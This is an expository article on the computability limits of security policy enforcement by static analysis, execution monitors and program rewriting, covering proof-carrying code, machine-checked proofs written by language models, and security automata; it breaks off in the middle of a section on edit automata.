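# Which policies can be enforced by static analysis, execution monitoring and program rewriting

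## Programs, policies and degrees of undecidability

Computers routinely run programs that their owners did not write and have little reason to trust. Web browsers download and run small programs, and operating systems load drivers from device makers. A security policy divides programs into those that behave acceptably and those that do not, and an enforcement mechanism prevents untrusted programs from violating the policy. The practical question is what such a mechanism can guarantee about every program, including one written to defeat it.

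Mechanisms come in three kinds. A static analysis examines the program before it runs and accepts or rejects it in finite time, as a Java virtual machine does when it type-checks code it is about to load. An execution monitor observes the program's security-relevant steps as it runs and intervenes before a forbidden one, as an operating system does when it stops a user from opening a file without permission. A program rewriter changes the program before it runs so that it satisfies the policy, for instance by inserting a bounds check before every instruction that accesses memory.

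A mechanism that blocks everything keeps every program within every policy, but it is useless. In *Security Policy Enforcement by Automated Program-Rewriting*, Hamlen (2006) therefore reserves the word "enforce" for precise enforcement, which prevents all the behavior a policy forbids and permits all the rest. An overcautious mechanism precisely enforces some other, stricter policy, and comparing that policy with the intended one shows how much acceptable behavior the mechanism blocks.

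The theory began with monitors. In 2000, Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* showed that a monitor that observes only the steps a program has taken so far can enforce only safety properties, which require that some "bad thing" never happens and whose violations show up after finitely many steps. Schneider left program analysis and program modification outside his definition and named them as further classes to study. The same year, Viswanathan's doctoral thesis, *Foundations for the run-time analysis of software systems*, added the requirement that a monitor be able to compute whether the steps so far amount to a violation. In 2006, Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider's *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* put static analysis, execution monitoring and program rewriting into one model. It proved that rewriting can enforce policies that no monitor can, and found that the class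 of policies Schneider and Viswanathan had assigned to monitors was too large.

### A machine with three tapes

Enforcement has fundamental limits because an enforcement mechanism is itself a program, usually running on a computer no more powerful than the one that runs the untrusted code. To prove these limits, Hamlen and colleagues represent the untrusted program as a Turing machine, a finite table of rules for reading and writing symbols on an unbounded tape, which can compute anything an ordinary computer can. The textbook version takes a finite input and answers yes or no. It suits this purpose poorly because an operating system is meant to keep running without ever giving an answer, and because a single tape mixes what an outsider can observe with what only the program can access. Hamlen and colleagues instead use a variant with three tapes, called the program machine.

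The input tape, which may be infinitely long, holds everything that becomes known only as the program runs, such as what a user types or how a random choice comes out. Because all randomness comes from this tape, the machine itself can be deterministic, so the same program always does the same thing on the same input. The work tape starts blank and is the program's private memory. The trace tape is write-only and holds the record that the enforcement mechanism observes. Each observable step is an event with a fixed code, which the machine automatically writes to the trace. If writing a 1 to memory is an event with the code 0001, then 0001 appears on the trace every time the program writes a 1, and the program cannot omit it.

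An execution is the whole sequence of events that a program produces on one input, and a prefix is its beginning up to some point. Hamlen and colleagues describe a small machine that adds one to a binary number written lowest digit first. Given 1101 (eleven), it writes 0011 (twelve) on its work tape. Its trace has one event for the program itself, then one for each symbol read (1, 1, 0, 1 and an end marker), then an "ended" event repeated forever. The result, 0011, never appears in the trace because writing to memory is not an event in this example.

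The model treats every complete execution as infinite, so when a program stops, its execution is padded by repeating the "ended" event forever. The theory depends on this treatment. If every execution were guaranteed to be finite, a mechanism could hold back all of a program's effects until the program finished, inspect the complete record, and then release or discard them. Any computable policy would be enforceable that way, and the differences between mechanisms would largely disappear.

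The first event is also unusual because it encodes the program's own text. To stop a bad step before it happens, a monitor has to look at least one step ahead for each symbol the program might read next, which requires the program's rules. Putting the text at the start of every trace supplies them. This assumption is generous, since Schneider's monitors had no such information by definition, and the monitors inside real operating systems make little use of it; they typically react to single instructions through hardware interrupts. Hamlen and colleagues conjecture that a model with less access to the text would change their results only trivially. Access to the text also helps a monitor less than it might seem to, because the monitor has only finite time at each step to analyze it.

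Enforcement can fail for two different reasons. The mechanism may be unable to observe the events that matter, in which case replacing it with a cleverer one that observes the same events does not help. Or it may have the information it needs but be unable to compute the answer, in which case a different kind of mechanism might succeed.

The first kind of failure is very common in practice. For example, a policy might forbid a program from sending a message after it has read a file. Schneider points out that a system may offer many ways to send a message, some buried deep inside it, and a monitor that misses one enforces nothing of interest. Kannan, Kim and colleagues (2019) make a related complaint about their own field, runtime monitoring, in *A Retrospective Look at the Monitoring and Checking (MaC) Framework*. Most approaches start from a given trace and don't address whether it is the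 right one. In MaC, which checks Java programs as they run, the user has to specify which method calls and variable changes make up each event.

The 2006 model mostly avoids this problem. The trace contains the program's text and every input symbol it reads, and the machine is deterministic, so a mechanism can in principle reconstruct the private work tape up to the current step. In the adding example, it could compute 0011. The theorems are therefore almost entirely about the second kind of failure, and anyone applying them to a real system has to check separately that the system's events are the right ones.

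### Policies and detectors

Formally, a security policy *P* is a division of all programs into those that satisfy it and those that do not. Nothing in this definition requires the division to be reasonable or easy to compute. Often, though, the natural way to state a policy is to describe which single executions are acceptable. A test of that kind is a detector, and it induces a policy as follows:

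*P*(*M*) holds exactly when every execution of program *M*, over all possible inputs, passes the detector.

For the rule about files and messages, the detector scans an execution and rejects it if a "send" event comes anywhere after a "file read" event. A program satisfies the policy if no possible input leads to a rejected execution, including inputs that nobody may ever supply.

Rules about access to files and devices usually have this form. So do rules about availability, such as a requirement that a server eventually answers each request, although the detector may then need to consider an entire infinite execution. Rules about the flow of information do not have this form. Suppose a program holds a secret bit and prints an unrelated random bit. It has four possible runs, since the secret and the printed bit can each be 0 or 1, and someone who sees the output learns nothing about the secret.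 A second program prints the secret itself. Its only two runs, 0 with 0 and 1 with 1, match two of the first program's runs in both secret and output. Any test on single runs that passes the first program must therefore pass the second, even though the second program reveals the secret. The second program is insecure because the other two runs are missing, which no single run can show. A requirement on the whole set of executions is called a hyperproperty.

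That argument assumes that an execution contains only outward steps. It applies slightly less cleanly to the 2006 model, where each execution begins with the text of its program. One can then define a detector that ignores everything after the first event and passes the execution if the program as a whole complies. Such a detector exists in principle for any policy, so the remaining obstacle is how hard it is to compute.

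### The halting problem and the levels of difficulty

The halting problem, which Alan Turing posed in the 1930s, is the basic example of a question that no algorithm can answer. The problem is to decide whether a given program eventually stops on a given input. The Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *Recursive Functions* sets out the proof in full. Suppose a program *H* always answered this question correctly. We could then build another program, *G*, which takes the text of any program and uses *H* to find out whether that program halts when given its own text as input. *G* then does the reverse, looping forever if the answer is yes and halting if it is no. Suppose we run *G* on its own text. If *G* halts, then *H* answered that it does not, and if *G* loops, then *H* answered that it halts. *H* is wrong in both cases, so no such *H* exists.

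The proof rules out any single method that decides, for every program, whether it halts. Particular cases can still be settled, and many programs obviously halt or obviously do not. But a mechanism that must handle arbitrary untrusted programs needs a method that works for all of them.

In *Computational Analysis of Run-time Monitoring*, Kim, Kannan and colleagues (2002) turn the halting problem into a rule about single executions. A program emits the symbols 0, 1, *a* and *b*. Whenever it emits a string *x*, then *a*, then a string *y*, and then *b* forever, the rule requires that the Turing machine encoded by *x* halts on input *y*. If that machine does not halt, the violation is complete at the first *b*, and the monitor has seen every relevant symbol. But a monitor that could recognize all such violations would be establishing that machines never halt, which no algorithm can do in general.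 The rule is therefore a safety property in Schneider's sense that no monitor can check, which is why Viswanathan's extra condition matters.

Some undecidable questions are harder than others, and logicians sort them into the levels of the arithmetic hierarchy. A policy amounts to a yes-or-no question about programs, so policies can be sorted the same way. The discussion below needs only four levels.

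The lowest class contains the decidable policies, for which some algorithm always halts with the right answer. One example is "The program terminates within 100 steps." A program can read at most 100 input symbols in 100 steps, so one can check the policy by running the program for 100 steps on every input of that length. With a two-symbol alphabet, this takes 2^100 runs, or roughly 10^30, which is too many to carry out in practice. The policy is still decidable because the procedure is finite, and the classification concerns only what is possible in principle, regardless of the computing resources required.

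The next class is the recursively enumerable (RE) policies. For these, an algorithm can confirm in finite time that a program satisfies the policy, but it may run forever if the program does not. An example is "the program halts on at least one input". An algorithm can check this by running the program for one step on every input of length at most one, then for two steps on every input of length at most two, and so on. If the program halts on some input, this search eventually finds it. Otherwise, the search runs forever without establishing that no such input exists.

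A policy is co-recursively enumerable (coRE) if an algorithm can detect every violation in finite time, though it may run forever when there is none. "The program never halts on any input" is coRE because the same search will find an input on which the program halts, if there is one, and that input now shows a violation. Emil Post showed in 1944 that a policy that is both RE and coRE is decidable, because one can alternate between the two searches and one of them must stop. Neither of these two examples is both RE and coRE, because a method for deciding either would solve the halting problem. To find out whether a given program halts on a given input, one could build a second program that ignores its own input and runs the first on that given input, then apply the method to the second program.

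Π₂ (Pi-2) is the level beyond these, where in general a finite search can establish neither a "yes" nor a "no". The standard example is "the program halts on every whole-number input". Confirming this would take infinitely many checks, one for each number. Refuting it takes only one number on which the program runs forever, but watching a program for a finite time cannot show that it will run forever. The statement has the form "*for every* input *there is* a number of steps after which the program halts", whereas an RE statement needs only a "there is" and a coRE statement only a "for every". Whether two programs halt on exactly the same inputs is also a Π₂ question. This matters for rewriting because the rewritten program has to count as equivalent to the original whenever the original already complied with the policy.

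### Two running examples

Two policies from Hamlen and colleagues recur throughout the theory. One is the boot-sector policy, which a program satisfies if it never writes to any of cells 0 to 511 of the work tape, on any input. These cells represent the boot sector of a hard disk, the part a computer reads when it starts up. Every write to a cell is an event that identifies the cell.

The secret-file policy applies to a directory containing a file whose existence must stay secret. Untrusted programs can retrieve a listing of the directory. A program satisfies the policy if it behaves exactly as it would without the file, however many times it retrieves the listing.

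## Static analysis before the program runs

A program runs only if it passes the static analysis, and it then runs without interference. Hamlen and colleagues call a policy *P* statically enforceable if some Turing machine takes the text of any program *M* and always halts, accepting if *P*(*M*) holds and rejecting if it does not. This is also the definition of a decidable policy, which immediately proves the theorem that the statically enforceable policies are exactly the decidable ones. The definition allows the analyzer to simulate the program, provided the simulation always ends with an answer.

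### What an analyzer can decide

Static analysis can decide whether a program halts within 100 steps, even though some inputs are infinitely long, because only the first 100 input symbols can affect those steps. It can decide whether a program writes no output within its first 20 steps for the same reason. To decide whether a program has fewer than one million states, the analyzer can count the states in the program's text without simulating it.

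The argument fails without a limit on the number of steps. Hamlen and colleagues give three examples of policies that no static analysis can enforce: "the program eventually halts", "the program never halts" and "the program writes no output on input σ". The last policy concerns only one input, but no fixed number of steps is enough for the analyzer to rule out later output.

The boot-sector policy, which forbids writing to cells 0 to 511 of the work tape, has no step limit either. A checker for it would solve the halting problem. To see this, take any program *N* and any finite input *x*, and build a program *M* that works as follows:

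1. *M* ignores its own input tape. Its rules contain *x*, and it supplies those symbols whenever *N* would read input.
2. *M* simulates *N* on *x*, shifting all of *N*'s memory up so that it occupies only cells 512 and above.
3. If the simulated *N* halts, *M* writes a 1 to cell 0 and then halts too.

The head must pass over the boot sector to reach cell 512, so in this construction a step counts as a write only if it changes a cell.

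The simulation never touches the boot sector, so *M* violates the policy exactly when *N* halts on *x*. Building *M* is mechanical and doesn't require running *N*. A checker for the boot-sector policy could therefore be used to decide whether *N* halts on *x*, since it would reject *M* if *N* halts and accept *M* if *N* runs forever. No algorithm can decide this for every *N* and *x*, so no such checker exists.

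The same construction works for events that don't involve cell 0. If its last step instead sends a message or opens a file, it shows that no static analysis can determine, for every program, whether that event ever occurs.

Henry Gordon Rice proved a more general result in his 1951 doctoral dissertation. Rice's theorem concerns properties of a program's input-output behavior, meaning which inputs it halts on and what it outputs for them. If some programs have such a property and others lack it, the property is undecidable.

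The proof reuses the same trick. Let *L* be a program that runs forever on every input. Suppose *L* lacks the property, and let *W* be any program that has it. Given *N* and *x*, we can build a program that runs *N* on *x*, discards the result, then runs *W* on its own input. If *N* halts on *x*, the new program behaves like *W* and has the property. If *N* doesn't halt, the new program never reaches *W*, so it behaves like *L* and lacks the property. Deciding the property would therefore decide the halting problem. If *L* has the property, we use a *W* that lacks it, and the new program has the property exactly when *N* doesn't halt on *x*.

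The theorem does not cover several kinds of policy. A policy that every program satisfies, or that none does, is trivially decidable. So are many policies about the program's text, such as the limit on its number of states. The theorem also does not cover policies about a bounded part of a run, because two programs can have the same input-output behavior while one takes 90 steps and the other takes 200. The boot-sector policy is outside its scope too, since two programs can give identical outputs although only one of them writes to cell 0. That policy is still undecidable, as the separate proof above shows.

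### Rejecting some good programs

Many of the properties that compilers guarantee before a program runs are undecidable. Compilers can guarantee them because they also reject some programs that would have behaved well. Suppose a program stores a string in a variable meant for numbers, but only in a branch that no input ever reaches. The program never misuses the variable when it runs, but a typical type checker rejects it anyway, because the checker examines every branch without working out whether the branch is reachable. It accepts only programs in which every branch follows the typing rules, which is a decidable property of the source code.

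A conservative approximation is a decidable policy that is stricter than the intended one and lets no violations through. Hamlen and colleagues illustrate it with the policy "the program eventually halts". An analyzer can prevent violations by accepting only programs that halt within 100 steps, but it then rejects a harmless program that needs 101. With a limit of a million steps, it would accept many more programs but still reject some that halt.

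Every conservative checker, meaning one that lets no violations through, wrongly rejects infinitely many compliant programs if the policy is undecidable. If it wrongly rejected only finitely many, one could list those programs as exceptions for the checker to accept. The new checker would then decide the policy, which is impossible. There is also no best conservative checker for such a policy, because adding one wrongly rejected program to the exceptions always gives a slightly better one.

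Approximation does not change the class of statically enforceable policies, because the checker precisely enforces a stricter policy that was already decidable.

The stricter policy can still be very useful, including for requirements that no test on single runs can express. Hamlen and colleagues mention JFlow, which uses static analysis to provide guarantees about information flow. An analyzer can examine the whole program, so it can reject any program in which a secret might influence the output. This rule also rejects some programs in which the secret makes no difference to the output.

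### Proof-carrying code

A checker often rejects a safe program only because it cannot find the reason the program is safe, which the program's author may know. In *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, Necula and Lee (1996) proposed proof-carrying code, a method in which the program's author supplies that reason as a formal proof. They proposed it for an operating system's kernel, the core part with full access to the machine, which has to run code from untrusted applications.

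The consumer, who will run the code, first defines and publishes a safety policy. The producer then writes the program and derives from its machine code a verification condition, which is a logical formula whose truth guarantees that the code obeys the policy. *review proof carrying code* (2020), a summary of a later paper by Necula, calls this stage certification. It ends when the producer obtains a proof of the formula and attaches it to the code. In the validation stage, the consumer checks that the proof is valid, concerns this particular code, and establishes the required policy. The code then runs without further checks.

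For example, suppose a network packet filter first tests whether a packet has at least 14 bytes and, if so, reads the byte at position 12, counting from zero. If the policy forbids reading past the end of a packet, the verification condition is "if the length is at least 14, then 12 is less than the length", which takes one line to prove. Loops make the proof much harder because the producer usually has to find an invariant, a fact that remains true on every pass through the loop, and no general method always finds a suitable one.

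Necula and Lee tried the method on several packet filters written in hand-tuned assembly language. The proofs had to be validated only once, which took 1 to 3 milliseconds, and the filters then ran with no overhead. They were faster than filters built with the alternatives of the time, including safe programming languages and a technique that inserts memory checks into the code. The main practical difficulty was generating the proofs.

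The consumer doesn't need to trust the producer or the tool that found the proof. If someone tampers with the code on its way to the consumer, either the proof fails and the consumer rejects the package, or the proof still holds and the altered code is safe too. The consumer must trust its own proof checker, but Hamlen and colleagues note that people generally consider such checkers easier to get right than programs that construct proofs.

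Proof-carrying code can give a consumer a firm guarantee that a program never writes to the boot sector. This is consistent with the undecidability results because the consumer only has to check whether a supplied proof establishes that the code complies, rather than decide compliance from the code alone. The check takes a finite number of mechanical steps. In Hamlen and colleagues' classification, the policies a consumer can enforce are thus the decidable properties of code-proof pairs, some of which correspond to policies that are undecidable for code alone.

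The producer, who starts with code and no proof, faces a different problem. A proof is a finite string of symbols, so one can in principle list all possible proofs, shortest first, and check each one against the code. If a suitable proof exists, the search eventually finds it. Otherwise the search runs forever. The policies for which every compliant program has a proof are therefore the recursively enumerable ones. "The program halts on at least one input" is such a policy, because a record of one halting run is all the proof anyone needs. (Certifying compilers, which produce code and proof together, may also change what the program does, and that makes them a kind of program rewriter.)

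The boot-sector policy is coRE, because a search through all inputs will find a forbidden write if there is one. The construction with *N* and *M* shows that it is undecidable, so by Post's result it cannot also be recursively enumerable. But it would be recursively enumerable if every compliant program had a proof of compliance in a sound logic whose proofs a machine can check. So in any such logic, some compliant programs have no proof of compliance, and the consumer has to reject them along with the violators.

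### Proofs written by language models

Finding proofs took so much work that, for a long time, only a few important programs had this kind of guarantee. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026) reports that verifying seL4, a small operating system kernel, took about 20 person-years and 200,000 lines of proof. Verifying the C compiler CompCert took about 3 person-years.

Language models have now made proofs much easier to find. They suit the job because it doesn't matter how often they are wrong; the proof checker rejects any invalid proof and the model has to try again (Kleppmann 2025, *Prediction*). Like the producer in Necula and Lee's work, a language model doesn't have to be trusted.

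Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes the largest demonstration so far. Anthropic and the company Theorem used Claude, Anthropic's model, to prove security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that tests software by feeding it large numbers of generated inputs. According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026), the proofs cover 239 test programs and took a few weeks. Each proof establishes that a program exits normally, without a crash, memory error or failed assertion, on every input smaller than 64 megabytes. The kernel of the Rocq proof assistant, the small core that checks each step, accepted the proofs.

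A Russian news report, OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), gives the total as about 180 million lines of proof. That works out at about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 machine instructions, or more than 30 lines per instruction. In the process, Claude found and fixed hundreds of bugs that the existing tests had missed.

These proofs hold for a model in which a single-threaded program runs on a RISC-V processor with a fixed amount of memory, and Linux behaves according to a formal description. They do not cover bugs that involve several threads or faulty hardware, or parts of the libraries that the test programs never call.

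The property is decidable in principle, just like "halts within 100 steps", because the inputs and the memory are both bounded. Checking it by brute force is infeasible, since it would need more than 2^500,000,000 runs. The only advantage of the proofs here is that they require little enough computation to be carried out.

Other results from 2026 support this. In *Scaling Lean Theorem Proving for Real-World Code Verification* (2026), an agent built on an off-the-shelf model proved or refuted 597 of 600 verification conditions from one benchmark and all 189 tasks from another, with every result checked by the proof assistant Lean. *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification* (2026) describes a general coding agent that proved every lemma its developers targeted, without help from proof experts. Its main target was Iris, a library for reasoning about programs whose parts run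 at the same time and share memory. In *Machine-Generated, Machine-Checked Proofs for a Verified Compiler (Experience Report)* (2026), Claude Code proved one stage of a compiler correct. The researchers guided it and reviewed its work but wrote none of the proof.

Pairing a language model with a proof checker doesn't make an undecidable policy decidable. The pair is still an algorithm, and some compliant programs have no proof for it to find. When it fails, the program may violate the policy, the proof may be too hard for this model, or the program may comply but have no proof. The failure alone doesn't show which of these is true. Anthropic also had some test programs it could not prove safe.

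The limit may matter less in practice than it seems to. The theorem is about deciding every program that anyone might submit, but a producer needs only one version that does the job and has a proof, and can rewrite the code until it has one. This is much more realistic when proofs are easy to produce, so a consumer can then reasonably reject every program that arrives without a proof.

A proof also guarantees only what its specification states. In *SWE-Proof*, Ma, Mikek and colleagues (2026) built a formal specification, an implementation and a machine-checked proof for each of 500 real programming tasks, mostly bug reports. When they tested Claude Opus 4.8, about a quarter of its patches that passed every hidden test were still wrong on some input. Giving the model a correct formal specification raised the share of tasks it solved from 85% to 95%, but asking it to write its own did not improve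 the result. Only 56% of the specifications it wrote passed an audit.

The most common fault was a specification that covered only part of the required behavior. One of the 500 tasks concerns a chart whose edges were cut off. The correct specification requires the frame to contain every point and each side of the frame to touch a point. With only the first requirement, a program that drew a frame far too large would satisfy the specification, and the proof would still be valid.

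This is less of a problem for security policies than for correctness in general. "Never write to the boot sector" applies to every program, so people can write it once and examine it carefully. Each bug fix needs its own specification.

### Checking beforehand or watching as it runs

Static analysis has some practical advantages over monitoring, even for a policy that both can enforce. It adds nothing to the running time, whereas a monitor's checks usually slow the program down. It also warns of violations before the program runs. Hamlen and colleagues point out that a monitor may detect a violation only on some runs and arbitrarily late, so the system may have to undo a half-finished computation. This may be impossible if the program moves money or controls a machine.

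The main drawback of static analysis is that it rejects some good programs. Even an exact analysis rejects a whole program because of what it would do on one input, although that input may never occur. A monitor lets the program run and intervenes only if the bad step is about to happen. Some decidable policies are also simpler to check at run time, and a simpler mechanism is less likely to contain mistakes. The two mechanisms may also have different information available. If the analyzer receives the source code and the monitor receives only the compiled program, which has lost some of that information, each may be able to enforce policies that the other cannot.

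Many systems combine static analysis with checks at run time. The Java virtual machine checks most types before a program starts and leaves some checks until it runs. *VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) combines the two for AI agents, which are language models that act through software tools. A model writes a short function that decides whether an action is allowed, and a static verifier proves that the function meets its formal specification. The function then checks each action before the agent carries it out. The proof covers a small piece of ordinary code, which is far easier to verify than the agent. It doesn't cover the earlier step, in which another language model extracts the function's inputs from the agent's data.

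## Execution monitoring while the program runs

An execution monitor only has to check each event just before it takes effect, rather than work out everything a program might do, as a static analysis must.

The monitor in Schneider's theory is deliberately simple. It observes the steps of a single execution, and it can respond to a violation only by terminating the program. It has no access to the program's text, so it can't calculate what the program will do next or what it would have done with different input.

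### Security automata

Schneider models such a monitor as a security automaton, which has four parts:

- a set *Q* of states, which may be infinite as long as one can number them
- a set *Q*₀ of initial states, taken from *Q*
- a set *I* of input symbols, which represent the steps the monitor can observe
- a transition function *δ*, which gives, for each state and input symbol, the set of states the automaton can move to

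The automaton can be in several states at once. It starts in all the states of *Q*₀. Each time it reads a symbol, it applies *δ* to every current state and moves to all the resulting states. If there are none, it rejects the sequence. It never has to reach a final state, so it can also process executions that never end.

The rule that a program must not send a message after it has read a file needs only two states, "nothing read" and "file read". The automaton starts in "nothing read". A FileRead event takes it to "file read", and every other event leaves it where it is. Once it is in "file read", it has a transition for every event except Send. Suppose a program is about to produce the events Send, FileRead, Compute, Send:

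| Event about to happen | Current state | Next state | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Send | nothing read | nothing read | the event goes ahead |
| FileRead | nothing read | file read | the event goes ahead |
| Compute | file read | file read | the event goes ahead |
| Send | file read | none | the monitor terminates the program |

To enforce the rule, the monitor runs the automaton alongside the program and feeds it each step the program is about to take. If the automaton has a transition for that step, the step goes ahead. Otherwise the monitor terminates the program before the step takes effect. In this example, the monitor allows the first message and terminates the program before it sends the second.

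Other policies need richer states. In Schneider's example of access control, the state is a record of who has which rights to which objects. The automaton has a transition for an operation only if the record contains the right it needs, and events that grant or revoke rights change the record. A few policies need unlimited memory. For example, if a variable must always equal the sum of its earlier values, the automaton has to store a total that can grow forever. Schneider notes, however, that the policies of real systems don't seem to need much storage.

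Running the automaton for every machine instruction would be slow, but a monitor can skip any event that would leave the automaton's state unchanged. Memory-protection hardware, for example, interrupts the program only when an access falls outside the permitted range, so it adds almost no time to ordinary accesses.

The scheme assumes that the program cannot tamper with the automaton and that the monitor can stop any event it needs to stop. But a monitor cannot stop a clock tick, as *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (Basin, Jugé and colleagues) points out.

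### Safety properties

Schneider's monitor can enforce only safety properties. It observes one execution, so its policy must be a test on single executions. It cannot observe future events, so it must stop the program as soon as the events so far fail the test. It must do so even if some continuation would have passed, because the program might end right there. It can also reject an execution only after finitely many events. A policy that meets these constraints is a safety property, meaning that every violation appears in a finite prefix that no later event can repair.

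Suppose a customer pays a seller for a service. "After the payment, the seller does nothing except provide the service" is a safety property, because any other action by the seller violates it immediately. A seller who takes the money and then does nothing still complies with it. "The seller eventually provides the service" is not a safety property, because the service may still come however long the customer has waited, so no finite prefix of the execution violates it.

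Terminating an execution never breaks a safety property, because it only removes behavior. Several monitors can therefore run side by side and enforce all of their policies at once. Removing behavior can, however, break a requirement on information flow. For example, a program that ignores its secret bit and outputs a random bit has four possible runs. Removing the two in which the output differs from the secret leaves a program that reveals the secret.

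### The four conditions

Hamlen and colleagues restate Schneider's requirements for their program machine and add one from Viswanathan. Let *χ* (chi) be an execution or a prefix of one, |*χ*| its length, and *χ*[..*i*] its first *i* events. *D*(*χ*) means that *χ* passes the detector *D*. A policy *P* belongs to the class if there is a detector *D* that meets all four of these conditions:

- EM1: *P*(*M*) ⇔ *D*(*χ*) for every execution *χ* of *M*. A program satisfies the policy exactly when all its executions pass.
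- EM2: *D*(*χ*) ⇒ *D*(*χ*[..*i*]) for every *i* with 1 ≤ *i* < |*χ*|. If an execution passes, so do all its prefixes, which means that a bad beginning can never turn into a good execution.
- EM3: not *D*(*χ*) ⇒ there is an *i* ≥ 1 such that not *D*(*χ*[..*i*]). If an execution fails, one of its finite prefixes already fails.
- EM4: *D*(*χ*) is decidable whenever *χ* is finite. An algorithm can always tell, in finite time, whether the events so far pass.

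Viswanathan added EM4, the requirement that *D* always finish with an answer, which Schneider had left implicit. Before each event, a monitor for such a policy applies *D* to the events so far plus the new one, and intervenes if *D* rejects the sequence. Without EM4, this check might never finish. For example, if a policy requires every Turing machine a program names to halt, the monitor could run forever trying to determine whether one does.

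### Why these are the coRE policies

Viswanathan also proved that the policies meeting all four conditions are exactly the coRE policies, those for which an algorithm can detect any violation in finite time. Hamlen and colleagues later proved the same result for their own model. Each direction of the proof is a short construction.

Suppose first that *P* meets the conditions with a detector *D*. We need an algorithm that halts on a program *M* if *M* violates *P* and runs forever otherwise. At each stage *n* = 1, 2, 3 and so on, the algorithm runs *M* for *n* steps on every input of length at most *n* and applies *D* to every prefix this produces. If *D* rejects one, the algorithm halts. Some inputs are infinitely long, but *M* can read at most *n* symbols in *n* steps, so the search eventually covers every finite prefix of every execution.

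Every stage finishes, because it tries finitely many inputs and each test is finite by EM4. If *M* violates *P*, then some execution fails by EM1, and some finite prefix of it fails by EM3, so the search reaches that prefix and halts. If *M* satisfies *P*, then all its executions pass by EM1, and all their prefixes pass by EM2, so the search runs forever. The search therefore halts exactly when *M* violates *P*, which means *P* is coRE.

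For the other direction, suppose *P* is coRE. Then there is an algorithm *V* that halts on the text of a program exactly when the program violates *P*. The first event of any execution contains the program's text, so a detector can run *V* on it. For finite *χ*, let *D*(*χ*) hold if *V* does not halt within |*χ*| steps on the program text in the first event of *χ*. For infinite *χ*, let *D*(*χ*) hold if *V* never halts on that text.

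This detector meets all four conditions:

- EM1 holds because complete executions are infinite. If *M* violates *P*, then *V* halts and all of *M*'s executions fail. If *M* satisfies *P*, then *V* never halts and they all pass.
- EM2 holds because if *V* has not halted after |*χ*| steps, it had not halted after fewer.
- EM3 holds because if *V* halts at all, it does so after some finite number of steps, and a prefix of that length fails.
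- EM4 holds because running *V* for |*χ*| steps takes finite time.

For example, suppose *V* needs 40 steps to detect that *M* violates the policy. Every execution of *M* then passes for its first 39 events and fails at the 40th, whatever the input and whatever *M* is doing at that point. This detector suffices for the theorem, but *M* may have already done what the policy forbids at its tenth event, which suggests why this class proved too large for real monitors.

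### Static policies and the boot sector

Every decidable policy is coRE, so the theorem implies that monitors can enforce every statically enforceable policy. This also follows without the theorem, because a monitor with access to the program's text can run the static analysis itself, right after the program loads and produces its first event. The analysis always finishes, and the monitor terminates the program if the analysis rejects it.

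The class of policies that monitors can enforce is also strictly larger, because it contains the boot-sector policy, which no static analysis can enforce. A detector for this policy scans the events for a write to any of cells 0 to 511. It meets EM1 by definition, EM2 and EM3 because a forbidden write stays in the record and occurs after finitely many events, and EM4 because scanning a finite list takes finite time.

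To block the write rather than just record it, the monitor has to determine what the program will do next. It reconstructs the current state of the computation from the trace and simulates the next step. If that step reads input, the monitor simulates it once for each possible input symbol, which takes finite time because the alphabet is finite.

Suppose the program is about to read a symbol, and will write to cell 600 if it is 0 and to cell 5 if it is 1. In this model a single step can both read a symbol and write to a cell, so the monitor cannot block the write after the symbol is read. It must terminate the program before the read, even if the next symbol would have been 0. This never terminates a compliant program, because the policy covers all inputs and a program that would write to cell 5 on some input already violates it.

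An execution monitor only has to check whether the program's next step is allowed, while a static analyzer has to check every step the program will ever take. If the program never attempts a forbidden write, the monitor never has to prove this.

### What access to the program's text changes

The first event contains the program's text, so every policy *P*, however hard to compute, has the detector "the program that produced this execution satisfies *P*". Hamlen and colleagues use such a detector in one of their proofs for the policy that a program never halts.

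Such a detector meets EM1 because all executions of *M* pass if *M* satisfies *P* and all fail if it doesn't. It meets EM2 because a prefix has the same first event as the whole execution and so gets the same verdict. It meets EM3 because if an execution fails, the prefix containing only its first event fails as well. This holds for any *P*, so in this model EM1 to EM3 exclude no policies, and only EM4 restricts which ones can be enforced.

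This explains why Hamlen and colleagues say that the policy "the program eventually halts" meets EM1 to EM3 and fails only EM4, even though it is a standard example of a policy that is *not* a safety property. The policy meets the first three conditions if the detector uses the program's text. It fails EM2 if the detector looks for the "ended" event, because a run that halts at step 50 passes while its first 49 events do not.

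No detector for this policy can also meet EM4. If one did, the policy would be coRE, and some algorithm would find every program that fails to halt. For a program that ignores its input, we could run that algorithm and the program side by side. One of the two would stop, and we could decide whether the program halts by seeing which one did.

The detector "the program satisfies *P*" meets EM4 only if *P* is decidable. A policy that is coRE but undecidable needs a different detector, such as the one from the proof, which runs the violation-finder a little longer with each event. These monitors can enforce more policies than static analysis because they are allowed to postpone the verdict while the program runs.

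Schneider's monitor can't use any detector of this kind because it has to treat two programs alike if they produce the same steps. It can't even enforce "the program has fewer than one million states", which a monitor that can read the program's text could enforce by counting the states.

A monitor that has the program's text can also enforce some requirements that compare several executions. One example is the requirement that a secret input bit does not affect the program's output in its first 100 steps. Schneider's monitor cannot enforce it, because a single run doesn't show what the output would have been with the other bit. A monitor with the text can try both values of the bit with every combination of other input symbols that the program could read in 100 steps. There are finitely many combinations, so the monitor can decide at the first event whether the program meets the requirement.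 This method doesn't work without a limit on the number of steps.

Schneider's monitor cannot see the program's text, but it doesn't need to predict the next step, because the theory assumes that each step reaches the monitor before it takes effect. Ligatti (2006), in *Policy Enforcement via Program Monitoring*, observes that operating systems and virtual machines can usually access the whole program, whereas firewalls and network scanners cannot. Monitors that attach only to certain functions of the operating system also lack this access. For monitors without it, the relevant limit is Schneider's restriction to safety properties.

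### Monitors that edit the event stream

Terminating the program is a crude response, and many real monitors do something milder, such as skipping the event or adding a log entry. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2003), in *Edit Automata*, therefore treat a monitor as something that transforms a sequence of events. Its input is the sequence that the program attempts, and its output is the sequence that actually takes effect. They compare four types:

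- a truncation automaton can only terminate the program, like Schneider's monitor
- a suppression automaton can also drop single events
- an insertion automaton can terminate the program and add events
- an edit automaton can do all of these things

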